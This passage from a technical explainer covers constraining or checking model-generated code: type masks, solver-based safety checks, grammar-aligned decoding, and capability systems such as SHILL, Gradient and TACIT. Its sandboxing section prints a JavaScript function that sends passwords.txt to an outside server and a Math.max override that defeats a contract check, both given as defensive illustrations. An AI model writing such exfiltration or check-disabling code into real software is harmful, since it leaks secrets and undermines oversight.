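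The tool also requires some type annotations that TypeScript makes optional, and one of these prevents a common mistake. Without the tool, Gemma 2 9B used the list method reduce to build a list from an empty one. TypeScript inferred that the empty list could never contain anything and rejected the line that added a number to it. When the tool required a type for the list, the model wrote "acc: number[]" and the program compiled.

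### Results on six models

Mündler and colleagues tested six open models with 2 to 34 billion parameters on TypeScript versions of HumanEval and MBPP. The models wrote functions from descriptions (synthesis), translated them from Python, and used the compiler's error message to repair programs that had failed to compile. The researchers applied the mask only where the unconstrained program did not compile, and kept the other programs unchanged.

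Type errors made up 94% of compilation errors, so even a perfect grammar would have removed only 9.0% of these errors in HumanEval synthesis and 4.9% in MBPP synthesis, on average across the models. The type mask removed 75.3% and 52.1%, respectively.

The table shows HumanEval synthesis, for which each model wrote 636 programs, four for each of 159 tasks.

| Model | Failed to compile, no mask | Failed to compile, mask | Passed tests, no mask | Passed tests, mask |
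|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemma 2 2B | 103 | 44 | 29.1% | 30.2% |
| Gemma 2 9B | 45 | 13 | 56.6% | 58.3% |
| Gemma 2 27B | 15 | 2 | 69.5% | 71.2% |
| DeepSeek Coder 33B | 26 | 5 | 68.9% | 71.1% |
| CodeLlama 34B | 86 | 28 | 41.0% | 43.4% |
| Qwen2.5 32B | 17 | 2 | 79.6% | 81.8% |

Pass rates rose much less than compilation errors fell, because most wrong programs already compiled. Only 17 of Qwen2.5 32B's programs failed to compile, so a perfect mask could have raised its pass rate by at most 2.7 percentage points. Over both sets of tasks, the mask made 21 more of the model's programs compile, and 15 of those also passed their tests.

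The average pass rate rose by a relative 3.5% in synthesis, 5.0% in translation and 37.0% in repair. Repair improved most because every task began with a program that did not compile and the models were poor at fixing such programs unaided. On HumanEval repair, Gemma 2 2B's pass rate rose from 11.6% to 20.9%, while DeepSeek Coder 33B's rose only from 47.6% to 50.7%.

The median time per synthesis task rose by 39.1% on HumanEval and 52.1% on MBPP. The extra time comes from running the automaton, because the mask seldom rejects a token. Even with Gemma 2 2B, the first token drawn was acceptable 99.4% of the time. Testing one proposed token at a time was essential, because testing the whole vocabulary at each step made every task exceed its five-minute limit.

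### Loops after a forced detour

A program that the model finishes under the mask should always compile. Mündler and colleagues traced the remaining compilation errors to programs that the model never finished. In one task, CodeLlama 34B treated a number from a list as a list and began to write ".sort". The mask excluded that, so the model wrote ".toString" instead. It then added slice, concat, split, reverse and join, one after another, until it ran out of tokens.

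Each of those steps was valid, and a valid ending was available throughout. But the model had made its mistake before it wrote ".sort", so excluding that token did not correct the mistake. Mündler and colleagues suggest limiting the complexity of expressions to stop such loops or steer the model out of them.

A type error may come from a mistake several lines earlier. In an example from *ChopChop*, a model declared a variable with `const`, which forbids later changes, then tried to reduce it by 1 inside a loop. A type mask blocks the assignment, but it cannot go back and change `const` to `let`. Models in this position often filled the rest of the program with blank space or comments. In the worst cases, they wrote arithmetic so deeply nested that the checker timed out.

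### How often do models make type errors?

The benefit of a type mask depends on how many type errors the model would otherwise make. *Learning to Guarantee Type Correctness in Code Generation through Type-Guided Program Synthesis* (2025) cites earlier studies in which type errors accounted for 33.6% of failed programs. Nogueira and colleagues found that missing imports and parameters of incompatible types caused most compilation errors in all the languages they compared.

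Stronger models make fewer such errors, at least in common languages. In *PROBE* (2026), code from the larger proprietary models failed to compile least often, and Rust had the highest rate of compilation failure of any language. *Idea First, Code Later* (2026) found that GPT-5 and Gemini 2.5 Pro made relatively few compilation errors on C++ programming contest tasks and failed mainly because their algorithms were wrong or too slow.

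Harder tasks can give the opposite result. In the difficult C-to-Rust translations described earlier, more than half of Claude Opus 4.8's first drafts failed to compile. None of these studies measured how often the frontier models of late 2026 make type errors in ordinary TypeScript. Such errors are probably rare in a small function like pickTop. A programmer can check by generating 50 or so functions of the kind the shop needs and counting the type errors the compiler reports.

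Compiler errors may also fall into a few groups. *Learning the Error Patterns of Language Models* (Kim, Berg-Kirkpatrick and D'Antoni, 2026) describes a system that collects 500 TypeScript programs from a model, sorts the faulty ones by compiler error, and has a larger model write short filters that recognize each error pattern in unfinished text. Qwen2.5 14B often assigned new values to const variables, while Qwen2.5 1.5B put import statements inside functions.

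Three filters caught 75.2% of the smaller Qwen model's faulty programs. Applying all of that model's filters raised the share of its programs that compiled by over 60%, to about the level of the much larger Llama 3.1 8B. For Gemma 3 12B, the filters caught only 4.0% of faulty programs, so not every model's errors follow such simple patterns.

A filter may reject valid text, as long as the model almost never writes it. One filter rejects any function body that starts with blank space. Such a body is legal, but Qwen2.5 1.5B wrote one almost only when it was about to leave the function empty. When a filter matches, the system abandons the draft and starts another that cannot begin the same way. This takes extra time, but the model may then avoid the original mistake instead of working around it.

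### The dynamic type under a mask

A type mask needs to know the types of the values in the program. If num has the dynamic type, any, the mask can exclude very little:

| Text after "parseInt(num" | num is a number | num is any |
|---|---|---|
| `;` | excluded | excluded |
| `ber` | excluded | excluded |
| `()` | excluded | allowed |
| `, 10)` | excluded | allowed |
| `.sort()` | excluded | allowed |
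| `.toString()` | allowed | allowed |

When an expression has a dynamic type, only the rules of grammar and scope still apply. The search would have to check whether the current type is consistent with the goal type, instead of identical to it. Because the dynamic type, ?, is consistent with every type, this check always succeeds before the search takes a step. Every member access or call on a dynamic value gives another dynamic value, so the loss of type constraints spreads to whatever the program computes from it.

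A partly known type still allows some checks. If score has the type (item: Product) => any, the mask can require its argument to be a Product, but it can't restrict what the program does with the result. Values of type any can easily enter the shop's code through JSON.parse, JavaScript's standard function for reading structured text, because its result type is any. If the sales figure in that text is the string "9", no mask can detect it. In a language with run-time casts, a cast to number would fail when the value arrives, but in TypeScript the programmer needs a contract like guard.

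Mündler and colleagues did not measure this effect. They left out six MBPP tasks whose signatures used the type any or lists of it, because those types were too broad. Their tool accepts type assertions, so a model could still return sales figures instead of products by writing "return figures as any;". A programmer who controls the grammar can remove the type any and all type assertions from it, so the model cannot write them. The shop should also give pickTop a precise signature before generation starts, because the mask takes the types of items, k and score from that signature.

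### Constraints that a programmer can write

The automaton of Mündler and colleagues enforces one set of rules, and adding a rule would require changing how it reads text. *ChopChop* separates enforcing rules from reading text. The programmer supplies a grammar and one or more pruners, which are functions that remove unwanted programs from a set, and the system handles the unfinished text.

For example, suppose a model must write a sum of odd numbers whose total is even, and has written "1+2". The system computes the set of all programs that begin this way. One pruner removes those that contain an even number, and another removes those with an odd total. If the model adds "+", the 2 is complete and even, so no programs remain and the mask excludes the token. If it adds another 2 to make "1+22", the mask allows the token because the 22 can still become 221, for a total of 222. The set of possible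 programs is usually infinite, but the system stores it in finite form using a description of sums that refers to itself.

In one case study, three small models had to rewrite a formula without changing its meaning. A list of algebraic rules, such as x + y = y + x, defined equivalence. Each model tried ten tasks at five temperatures. When the prompt asked for clearly marked code, 26 of the 150 unconstrained answers were equivalent to the original, compared with 39 under a grammar and 124 under the equivalence constraint. In one faulty answer, CodeLlama-7B rewrote start + (end − start) × scale but left out the final "+ start", an omission the equivalence constraint would have prevented.

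In the other case study, a pruner enforced types in a small part of TypeScript. No pruner can remove exactly the ill-typed programs, because the remaining set would have no finite description of the kind the system uses. This one keeps every well-typed program and lets some ill-typed ones through, whereas Mündler and colleagues made the opposite choice. Keeping every well-typed program is often better if a compiler will check the finished program anyway, because the compiler will report an ill-typed program but nothing will report that the mask blocked a correct one.

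The same three models then attempted 72 tasks at five temperatures, for a total of 1,080 programs per method:

| Method | Programs that compiled |
|---|---|
| No constraint | 781 (72%) |
| Grammar only | 651 (60%) |
| Type pruner | 932 (86%) |
| Tool by Mündler and colleagues | 1,035 (96%) |

The grammar lowered the number because it covered so little of the language that it excluded many programs that would have compiled. The type pruner worked within the same small grammar, which largely explains why the tool by Mündler and colleagues did better. The experiment measured only whether programs compiled, not whether they were correct. The type pruner added 64 to 204 milliseconds per token to the 81 milliseconds that CodeLlama-13B needed without it.

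### Division by zero and null pointers

Some faults depend on values as well as types. Maghera, Arya and colleagues (2026), in *AGDECODE*, describe a system that excludes three of them from C programs during generation: division by zero, use of a null pointer, and use of a variable that has no value yet. Their opening example contains two:

```c
void foo(int num) { int *x = malloc(sizeof(int)); *x = 16 / num;
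```

malloc returns a null pointer if no memory is available, and the code writes to x without checking for that. It also divides by num, which may be 0. All the types are correct, and no later text can repair either fault. The mask must therefore exclude the division unless the preceding code has ruled out zero, for example with "if (num == 0) return;".

AGDecode attaches facts to each part of the program, such as the values a variable may have at that point, and represents the unwritten parts as holes. It translates the facts and holes into logical formulas and passes them to Z3, an automatic solver, which determines whether any way of filling the holes makes the program safe. The system is sound and complete if the solver always finds the answer, but a real solver sometimes runs out of time. AGDecode can then reject the token, which may exclude valid code, or accept it and check the longer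 text later.

Maghera and colleagues accepted such tokens in their tests. They ran CodeLlama-13B on 77 tasks at three temperatures, with a limit of five seconds per check.

| Solver's answer | Share of checks | Median time |
|---|---|---|
| No safe completion | 39–46% | 1–2 milliseconds |
| A safe completion exists | 31–39% | 1.1–2.0 seconds |
| None within the limit | 22–25% | 5 seconds |

The researchers illustrate the effect with examples but do not report how many finished programs were safe, with or without the constraint. In one example, the model began its function with "assert(arr)", which stops the program if the pointer arr is null. The mask then allowed the code to read an element with "arr[". When the researchers deleted the assertion, the mask no longer allowed the bracket.

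The position of the excluded token affected whether the model could recover. After "arr", it could still turn the expression into a test such as "arr == NULL". If it had already written the star in "*arr", it had to dereference some pointer, because the system could not go back and remove the star, and the attempt almost always failed. The system also does not model the computer's memory, so it cannot generally rule out other memory errors.

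A similar constraint for JavaScript could stop the callback that divides a product's revenue by its visits from returning a score of Infinity. The mask would block the division until the code had tested for zero visits. This would prevent the error before the shop ran the function.

How long a check took depended more on where the text stopped than on its length. After "arr[i", the solver has to account for every expression that might begin with i, and most timeouts occurred at points like this. Once the statement is complete, i is just a variable and the check is simple. Maghera and colleagues therefore suggest checking at the ends of statements and going back if a check fails. This would avoid many of the slowest checks, but it requires undoing tokens, which their prototype cannot do.

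## Judge whether constraints during generation improve the program

Any program that a model finishes under a sound mask follows the mask's rules, but it may be worse than what the model would have written without the mask. When the mask excludes a token, the model has to continue from text it would seldom have produced itself, and the resulting program may be valid but wrong. Two evaluations of the same type mask on the same six models reached opposite conclusions about whether it helps.

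### How a mask distorts the choice

Suppose a model can begin the body of pickTop in two ways. Opening A, "const heap =", has a probability of 0.9 and nearly always leads the model to call a helper that it defines further down. Opening B, "const ranked =", has a probability of 0.1 and leads to an ordinary sort. The constraint forbids calling a function before its definition, so it accepts all of B's continuations but only 1% of A's, weighted by probability.

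A mask tests only whether an acceptable continuation exists. Both openings have one, so 90% of programs still begin with A. The mask then blocks the helper, and the model has to finish the program with a continuation to which it assigned a very low probability.

The alternative is to draw whole programs without a mask and discard the unacceptable ones. This gives a very different mixture:

```text
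accepted programs that begin with A:  0.9 × 0.01 = 0.009
accepted programs that begin with B:  0.1 × 1    = 0.1
share of A among accepted programs:   0.009 / 0.109 ≈ 8%
```

Discarding unacceptable drafts leaves the relative probabilities of the acceptable programs unchanged, which is an advantage if more probable programs are also better on average. But only 10.9% of drafts are acceptable, so each accepted program takes about nine drafts.

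Lew, Zhi-Xuan and colleagues (2023) gave an early example of the problem in *Sequential Monte Carlo Steering of Large Language Models using Probabilistic Programs*. They asked a model to continue "The Fed says" without any word longer than five letters. A mask blocked only tokens that would immediately break this rule, so the model could start the word "mortgage" but got stuck after "mortg".

A year later, Park, Wang and colleagues (2024), in *Grammar-Aligned Decoding*, stated the problem formally. Their goal is to produce only valid texts, in proportion to the probabilities that the model itself gives them. If s is the text so far and t a possible next token, the two methods differ in one factor:

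```text
aligned:  probability of t  ∝  p(t | s) × c(s + t)
masked:   probability of t  ∝  p(t | s) × (1 if c(s + t) > 0, otherwise 0)
```

Here c is the probability that the model, continuing without a mask, would end with a valid text. It is 0.01 after opening A and 1 after opening B, and a mask in effect treats both as 1. Calculating c exactly would require adding up the probabilities of all possible continuations, which is impractical for a real model.

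The distortion occurs even when the mask enforces exactly the right rules. Park and colleagues asked the model Mixtral 8x7B for a string of zeros and ones that ends in 1, and it did so about 90% of the time. They added a grammar that allows 00000 and every five-digit string that starts with 1. With the mask, only 30% of the strings ended in 1. The model chose 0 as its first digit about half the time, and after that 0 the grammar allowed only 00000.

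### Estimating what the mask ignores

Park and colleagues also proposed a remedy, ASAp, which learns c from earlier attempts at the same task. The first attempt uses an ordinary mask. ASAp then works backwards through the finished text and lowers its estimate of c wherever the model gave probability to excluded tokens. After a few drafts that begin with A, the estimate for A falls, so more of the later drafts begin with B. With enough drafts, the mixture converges to the aligned one.

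ASAp can converge very slowly. Park and colleagues drew 2,000 samples per task from Mistral 7B, and on some tasks the mixture had barely improved by the end. On bit-vector arithmetic tasks, ASAp gave correct answers 38% more often than a mask. On string-processing tasks that both methods could solve, it gave them 73% less often. Results for single tasks varied even more. ASAp raised the number of correct samples from 12 to 1,588 on one string task but lowered it from 363 to 69 on another, where the mask's bias happened to favour the most probable answer.

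Özgü, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *The Parser Already Knows*, estimate c in advance. For each grammar, they draw 1,000 texts without a mask, record the parser's state at every token, and note whether the finished text was valid. They train a small model to predict validity from these records and use its predictions to adjust the probabilities of the tokens that the mask allows. On grammars for bit-vector formulas and database queries, the resulting mixture was four to five times closer to the aligned one than masking's was, by a standard distance between distributions. The method took at most 25% longer than masking, whereas ASAp took up to 20 times as long. However, matching the model's preferences more closely produces better programs only if those preferences are good.

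### The type mask on every program

The type mask built by Mündler and colleagues raised pass rates in their own tests. Biagiola and colleagues tested it again on the same six models, this time applying it to every program. They used TypeScript versions of HumanEval and MBPP, three temperatures and ten runs of each combination, for a total of about 104,000 programs. They counted a program as a failure if the model did not finish it within 1,000 tokens or five minutes.

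The table gives their results for HumanEval at temperature 0.1, in percent.

| Model | Passed tests, no mask | Passed tests, mask | Compiled, no mask | Compiled, mask | Hit a limit, mask |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemma 2 2B | 35.7 | 32.0 | 91.8 | 90.7 | 6.4 |
| Gemma 2 9B | 58.4 | 50.5 | 92.6 | 92.7 | 7.6 |
| Gemma 2 27B | 70.4 | 67.6 | 98.3 | 94.6 | 4.8 |
| DeepSeek Coder 33B | 74.8 | 68.0 | 98.3 | 95.6 | 6.0 |
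| CodeLlama 34B | 50.3 | 46.5 | 92.6 | 94.9 | 4.4 |
| Qwen2.5 32B | 82.3 | 72.3 | 98.1 | 90.9 | 3.5 |

Every model passed fewer tests with the mask. The same was true at the other temperatures and on MBPP, where Biagiola and colleagues tested only the weakest and the strongest model. The difference was significant in all cases except Gemma 2 2B and CodeLlama 34B on HumanEval at temperature 1.0. In the CodeLlama case, the mask raised the share of programs that compiled from 85.5% to 92.0%, but the share that passed their tests fell from 40.8% to 39.4%.

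For four of the six models, the mask also lowered the share of programs that compiled, mainly because generation often hit a limit under the mask and almost never did without it. The tool also crashed on some programs. Qwen2.5 32B lost 10 points on the tests, of which 7.2 correspond to the drop in programs that compiled and 2.8 to additional programs that compiled but gave wrong answers.

Biagiola and colleagues also measured the probability each model assigned to the programs it had written. At temperature 0.1, the masked programs were significantly less probable than the unmasked ones on 22% of tasks, and more probable on only 2%. The programs that hit a limit were the least probable. For Gemma 2 2B, the masked and unmasked programs were about equally probable on tasks that it solved both with and without the mask.

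### Calls to functions defined later

Most of the harm came from the mask blocking valid programs. Biagiola and colleagues ran the mask's checker on 4,231 programs that Gemma 2 2B had written without a mask and that the TypeScript compiler had accepted. The checker rejected 982 of them, or 23%.

One of the 982 programs counts the even and odd palindromes up to a given number. Its main function calls isPalindrome, which is defined a few lines below. During masked generation, the mask blocked that name after the model had written "is", so the model completed it as isNaN, a built-in function that tests whether a value is "not a number". The model later began a helper named isN for the missing logic but never called it. The program compiles, and all its types are right. But isNaN is false for every number in the loop, so a count that depends on it never rises. In other cases, the same substitution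 sent the model into a loop until it reached a limit.

A mask could allow such calls by accepting any new name followed by a bracket and preventing the program from ending until it has defined that name. But the mask would then no longer catch invented function names as the model writes them, and it would have to check that the later definition fits every earlier call. Biagiola and colleagues note that handling such calls properly may require the system to undo tokens, which in the worst case is no faster than discarding whole programs.

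A programmer who has to use this mask could ask the model to define helpers such as byScore before the main function.

### Why the earlier evaluation found a gain

Mündler and colleagues used the mask only to regenerate programs that had failed to compile. For Qwen2.5 32B on HumanEval, 619 of the 636 programs compiled without the mask, so both columns of the comparison include them unchanged and don't show how the mask would have affected them. A program that does not compile fails its tests, so replacing it could raise the pass rate but not lower it.

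Their tool covers only part of TypeScript, so they chose this design to estimate the effect of a mask that covers all of it. This is reasonable, because a complete mask would accept every token of a program that compiles and so leave that program unchanged. But the masked method got a second attempt at each failed program and the unmasked method did not, so part of the gain may have come from trying again.

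| | Mündler and colleagues | Biagiola and colleagues |
|---|---|---|
| Programs written under the mask | only those that had failed to compile | all |
| What the result measures | the mask as a repair step, or roughly the benefit of a complete mask | the existing tool, left on all the time |
| Could the mask lower the pass rate? | no | yes |
| Qwen2.5 32B on HumanEval | 79.6% without, 81.8% with | 82.3% without, 72.3% with |

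The two results are therefore compatible. A programmer can also use the first design in practice by generating code without the mask, compiling it, and turning the mask on only after a failure.

### Three languages that should overlap

Biagiola and colleagues explain their results in terms of alignment, meaning the overlap of three sets of programs: those the model is likely to write, those the constraint allows, and those that are valid in the programming language. They define it as the number of programs in all three sets divided by the number in at least one.

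Nobody can calculate this fraction for a real language, which has infinitely many programs, but the definition helps identify when a constraint does harm. An unsound constraint does little harm if a compiler checks the program afterwards. An incomplete constraint does harm only if the model would have written the valid programs it excludes, so a mask that forbids classes does no harm to a model that never uses them.

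A programmer can reduce the harm by changing the model to write code the constraint allows, or by extending the constraint to cover the code the model writes.

### Training the model to fit the mask

Biagiola and colleagues tried the first approach on Gemma 2 2B and Qwen2.5 32B. They used reinforcement learning, which makes a model more likely to repeat outputs that receive a reward. The reward was 1 if the mask's checker accepted the program and 0 otherwise, whether or not the program solved the task. They trained on the tasks where the checker had rejected more than 90% of the model's programs. The table shows the percentage of programs generated at temperature 0.1 that passed their tests.

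| Model and tasks | No mask, before | Mask, before | No mask, after | Mask, after |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemma 2 2B, HumanEval | 35.7 | 32.0 | 32.8 | 32.1 |
| Gemma 2 2B, MBPP | 50.4 | 44.9 | 48.5 | 46.6 |
| Qwen2.5 32B, HumanEval | 82.3 | 72.3 | 82.0 | 77.6 |
| Qwen2.5 32B, MBPP | 79.5 | 70.1 | 80.1 | 76.3 |

Training recovered about half or more of what the larger model had lost, mainly because fewer programs hit a limit. On HumanEval, the gap between the small model's results with and without the mask almost closed, but only because its results without the mask got worse. The reward probably taught it to write programs that satisfied the checker without solving the task. The trained model with the mask did not match the original model without it in any of the four cases, even though the final tests included the tasks used for training.

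### A complete constraint

A complete mask for TypeScript would be very hard to build, so Biagiola and colleagues used TOML, a simple format for configuration files. They wrote a mask that allows everything in TOML's grammar, then made stricter versions that each removed one feature. Every file can be written without the removed feature. Three models each produced files for 100 tasks, ten times per task. The table shows the percentage of files that matched the reference file exactly.

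| Constraint | Gemma 2 2B | Qwen2.5 32B | Qwen3-Coder-Next 80B |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 31.3 | 40.3 | 62.5 |
| Complete grammar | 48.1 | 41.3 | 62.5 |
| No comments | 48.1 | 41.3 | 62.5 |
| No dotted keys, such as a.b = 1 | 48.8 | 41.3 | 63.0 |
| No optional spaces | 33.9 | 29.2 | 15.7 |
| No space before "=" | 28.6 | 39.7 | 1.9 |

The complete mask raised the small model's score by 54% in relative terms and the mid-sized model's by 2.5%. The largest model gained nothing, because it made almost no grammatical mistakes without the mask.

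Forbidding a single optional space cut the largest model's score from 62.5% to 1.9%, and most of its attempts ran out of time. The same rule hardly affected Qwen2.5 32B. A programmer therefore can't predict the harm by reading the grammar or judging how important the missing feature looks. A stronger model is not necessarily safer when the mask forbids some valid code.

Even with the complete mask, 6.6% of the TOML files that Qwen2.5 32B wrote were invalid. Without it, 102 out of 1,000 were invalid, and 66 of those had conflicting keys, a fault that TOML's grammar does not cover.

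### Writing the types along with the program

Huang, Zhang and colleagues (2025) argue in *TyFlow* that a mask can reject ill-typed code but doesn't teach the model about types. In their system, the model makes a series of decisions instead of writing text. Each decision applies a typing rule or fills in a name, and the system builds the program and the proof of its types together.

Suppose the program needs a number, and the names `score` and `product` are in scope. The model might choose the rule for a function call. The system then sets two smaller goals, a function that returns a number and an argument that this function accepts. The model meets them with `score` and `product`, which completes both the expression `score(product)` and the proof that it is a number. At each step the model receives the current goal along with the names and types in scope, so it does not have to find them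 in the earlier code. For training, a type checker converts existing programs into decisions like these.

Huang and colleagues trained two small models on Java and on SuFu, a research language with few existing programs. The share of SuFu tasks that the larger model (2 billion parameters) solved at the first attempt rose from 29.3% to 43.1%, and compilation errors fell from 61.2% to zero. In Java, the share solved rose from 17.9% to 23.2%, and compilation errors fell from 15.2% to 3.1%. The test sets were small, and the gain in SuFu was eight more tasks out of 58.

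A further test of the smaller model on SuFu suggests that the new notation was not enough by itself. Without any checks, the model solved 24.1% of tasks at the first attempt, the same as when it wrote ordinary text. Rejecting decisions that broke the grammar raised this to 27.6%, and rejecting those that broke the type rules raised it to 37.9%. Most of the improvement therefore came from rejecting invalid decisions, which is a kind of masking, although it suited a model trained to write in the new notation.

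The method requires retraining a model and defining the language's type rules for the system. The Java version leaves out lambda expressions, which programmers normally use for the comparison inside a sort, so it would be a poor fit for pickTop.

### Searching and going back

A search can undo a mistake that the model made several tokens earlier, which an ordinary mask can't do. In *AdapTrack*, Li and colleagues describe a system that goes back when the mask would have to exclude a large share of the possible next tokens, because the model has then probably made a mistake. When the task was to call the right library functions, this raised accuracy by up to 361% compared with an ordinary mask.

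*TreeCoder* (Princis, Sharma and David, 2026) compares several kinds of search and several checks in one system. The system stores unfinished programs as branches of a tree and scores each one, setting the score to zero if a check fails. The checks range from syntax to running the program on example tests. The table shows results for CodeLlama 7B on Python tasks from MBPP. "Combined" means syntax, example tests and a ban on comments.

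| Check | Search | Solved | Seconds per task |
|---|---|---|---|
| none | sampling | 32.3% | 2.3 |
| syntax | sampling | 34.0% | 2.4 |
| types and syntax | sampling | 47.5% | 27.1 |
| example tests | sampling | 60.0% | 3.9 |
| combined | sampling | 60.7% | 3.2 |
| combined | beam search | 63.0% | 16.1 |
| combined | Monte Carlo tree search | 65.3% | 78.4 |
| combined | ASAp | 68.9% | 84.1 |

Beam search keeps the few most probable unfinished programs at each step. The last two methods complete whole programs, then start again with better estimates of which branches work. This added as much as 8 points but took 26 times as long as sampling with the same checks.

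The example tests made a much larger difference than the choice of search. The final score includes these tests as well as hidden ones, which inflates every result that uses them. A programmer can get most of this benefit without a special decoder. When Princis and colleagues generated complete programs until one passed the combined checks, with up to five retries, the model solved 57.6% of tasks in 5.7 seconds each.

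The slower searches also lost their advantage under a time limit. With about ten seconds per task, ASAp solved 49.9% of the test tasks using the best settings found by automatic tuning, while plain sampling solved 49.6%. A faster method, which generates several programs side by side and replaces those that fail a check with copies of the others, solved 59.2%.

Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues instead give the model the reason its code is wrong. Their system closes off the unfinished program so that the language's ordinary compiler can read it, then passes any genuine error back to the model.

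### When to constrain and when to check afterwards

A programmer can choose a method from two measurements. The first is the share of about 50 drafts, generated without the mask, that fail to compile. This share limits how much the mask can help. The second is the number of drafts that compiled and passed their tests but that the mask's checker rejects. This number indicates how often the mask may block working programs.

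| Drafts that fail to compile | Good drafts that the mask rejects | Method |
|---|---|---|
| few | any number | generate freely, compile, and draw again after a failure |
| many | almost none | mask from the first token, then compile and test |
| many | some | generate freely, and use the mask only to replace drafts that fail |

Drawing again until a draft compiles is faster than using the type mask if fewer than roughly 30% of drafts fail. The mask increased the median time per task by 39% to 52%, while drawing again takes 1.1 drafts on average if 10% fail. This comparison assumes that each new draft has the same chance of success. If a model makes the same mistake every time, more drafts won't help, and the programmer should use the mask or send the model the compiler's error message.

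Masking from the first token suits narrow formats with a complete grammar, such as TOML, and closed lists, such as a database's columns or a company's approved packages. It also suits languages the model knows poorly. Ordinary TypeScript from a strong model probably belongs in the first row of the table.

The shop should still compile pickTop and run it behind guard on examples with known answers, whichever method produced the code. The program that called isNaN would have passed every type check.

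## Limit what generated code can reach

The following version of `pickTop` has the right type and returns the right products, so `guard` accepts every call:

```js
import { readFileSync } from "node:fs";

export const pickTop = (items, k, score) => {
  fetch(address, { method: "POST", body: readFileSync("passwords.txt") });
  return [...items].sort((a, b) => score(b) - score(a)).slice(0, k);
};
```

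It also sends the shop's passwords to whoever runs the server at `address`. A model can write such code by mistake or because of prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in something the model reads, such as a web page or a comment in a file.

### What a boundary contract does not cover

The guard function tests only what passes through its wrappers. On a server, any JavaScript module can import functions that read files or use the network, and those calls never pass through guard. The generated module can also change global variables that the shop's code relies on. Its code can run before guard has wrapped anything, because JavaScript runs a module's top-level code as soon as another module imports it.

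Time and memory are also outside the contract. If pickTop fills the computer's memory, the shop's program may crash before the postcondition runs.

Some language features even let code disable the checks:

```js
Math.max = () => -Infinity;
return [...items].sort((a, b) => score(a) - score(b)).slice(0, k);
```

JavaScript lets any module replace a built-in function for the whole program. The last clause of `guard` uses `Math.max` to find the best omitted score, so if generated code replaces `Math.max` with a function that always returns −Infinity, the reversed sort passes. Other languages have reflection, which lets a program look up fields and methods by name at run time, including some that the type checker would have stopped it from using. Code can also start an external program, which doesn't have to follow the language's rules.

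### Capabilities

Code has ambient authority if it can open a file just by naming it, because its access comes from the account it runs under. MIT's lecture notes *Capabilities and other protection mechanisms* describe how this can go wrong with a Fortran compiler that had permission to write in its own directory, where it kept a file of usage statistics. A user who had no right to change that file could name it as the place for the compiler's output, and the compiler would overwrite it. Security researchers call a program in this position a confused deputy.

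A capability is an unforgeable value that a program must hold to use a resource. If the compiler had required a capability for its output file, the user could have supplied only a file they were allowed to write.

In a capability-safe language, code can get a capability only from other code that already holds one. *Gradient* (Boruch-Gruszecki, Ghosn and colleagues, 2024) illustrates this with Log4j, a Java logging library that had a notorious security hole. Existing programs create a logger with no arguments. In a capability-safe version, they would have to pass it capabilities to use the file system, use the network and run new code. If an update started to need the capability to run new code, programs that used the library would stop compiling until someone decided to grant it.

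The caller can also pass a weaker capability, such as a wrapper around the file system that opens files only in the log directory. The callback score already works this way. If score looks up sales in a database, pickTop can trigger those lookups by calling score, but it can't send the database its own queries.

### Contracts that restrict capabilities

A contract can state what a function may do with a capability. *SHILL*, by Moore, Dimoulas and colleagues, describes a 2014 scripting language built on Racket's contract system. In one example, a function searches a directory for JPEG images and writes their paths to a file. Its contract allows it to list the directory, look up the entries and get their paths, but it may only append to the output file.

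SHILL enforces this with a wrapper around each capability. For example, it blames the function for trying to read the output file, and the caller for passing a file that does not allow appending. A script also can't reach anything above the directory, because SHILL doesn't let it look up a directory's parent.

Scripts often start other programs, which don't use contracts. SHILL runs these programs in a sandbox, where the operating system's kernel allows only what the script's capabilities allow. Moore and colleagues used this to grade students' programs with a 78-line script, including six lines for its contract. A program being graded could not read another student's work. The script took 1.13 times as long as an ordinary one.

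In all but three of the SHILL paper's tests, SHILL slowed tasks by at most 21%. The other three tasks took 1.7, 6.0 and 6.6 times as long. The task that slowed the most took under a second, and most of that time was spent starting Racket. The task that slowed the second most created over 15,000 sandboxes, nearly one for each file it searched.

Passing capabilities explicitly can become tedious. Even `cat`, a program that prints a file, needs eight capabilities for libraries and configuration files besides the obvious ones. SHILL therefore has functions that bundle the capabilities a program usually needs.

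*Extensible Access Control with Authorization Contracts*, by Moore, Dimoulas and colleagues, attaches rights to the context in which code runs instead of to the values it holds. Its contracts change those rights as execution crosses a boundary. Such a contract could remove the right to query the database when pickTop starts and restore it for each call to score. This works only if the database functions check for the right, so someone still has to find and protect every route to the database.

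### Moving a program to capabilities in stages

Most existing code assumes ambient authority, so switching to a capability-safe language usually means rewriting the whole program along with its libraries. Boruch-Gruszecki and colleagues propose gradual compartmentalization, which moves one component at a time, as gradual typing does with types. Gradient, their design for an extension of Scala, allows three kinds of component in one program:

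| Component | How it gets access | What limits its access |
|---|---|---|
| Unchecked package | by name, as before | a run-time monitor |
| Checked package | by name, as before | the compiler |
| Module | through its arguments | the capabilities its caller passes |

The compiler's check is called capture checking. It gives each type a capture set, which lists the capabilities that a value of that type may hold. For example, a logger that holds the file system `fs` has the type `Logger^{fs}`. A programmer can put a call to a checked package in a block that permits only `fs`, and the compiler rejects the program if the call could reach any other capability.

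An unchecked package has a special mark in place of capture sets, much as untyped code has the dynamic type in place of known types. The compiler accepts calls to the package only inside a block that limits what the package can access at run time. If the package tries to exceed the limit, the block stops with an error. The design relies on memory protection in the processor, so it also covers compiled code from other languages.

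The shop could run an unchecked pickTop in a block that allows no file or network access. The limit would also apply to score when pickTop calls it, so a score function that queries a database over the network would fail. The pickPositions version avoids this problem because the shop calculates the scores before the generated code starts.

Boruch-Gruszecki and colleagues converted Scala's standard XML library to a checked package to test how much work the middle stage takes. They changed about 260 of its 4,200 lines, and about 200 of those needed only a few added characters. They did not build the run-time monitor, but they used the overheads of an earlier system and their own counts of the relevant events to estimate its effect. They estimated that it would slow a program that reads many small XML files by 0.6% or 1.6%, depending on which processor feature the monitor used. The paper states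 a theorem that a program touches only the memory its capabilities allow, but the technical report proves a weaker version without that guarantee.

### Private data in checked code

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) applies capture checking to code written by models. Its system, TACIT, is for agents, models that carry out tasks using tools such as file access and web search. The agent submits Scala code instead of calling the tools directly, and TACIT runs the code only if it compiles.

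In this version of Scala, the type of a function shows which capabilities it may use:

```text
String -> Int         none
String ->{log} Int    only log
String => Int         any
```

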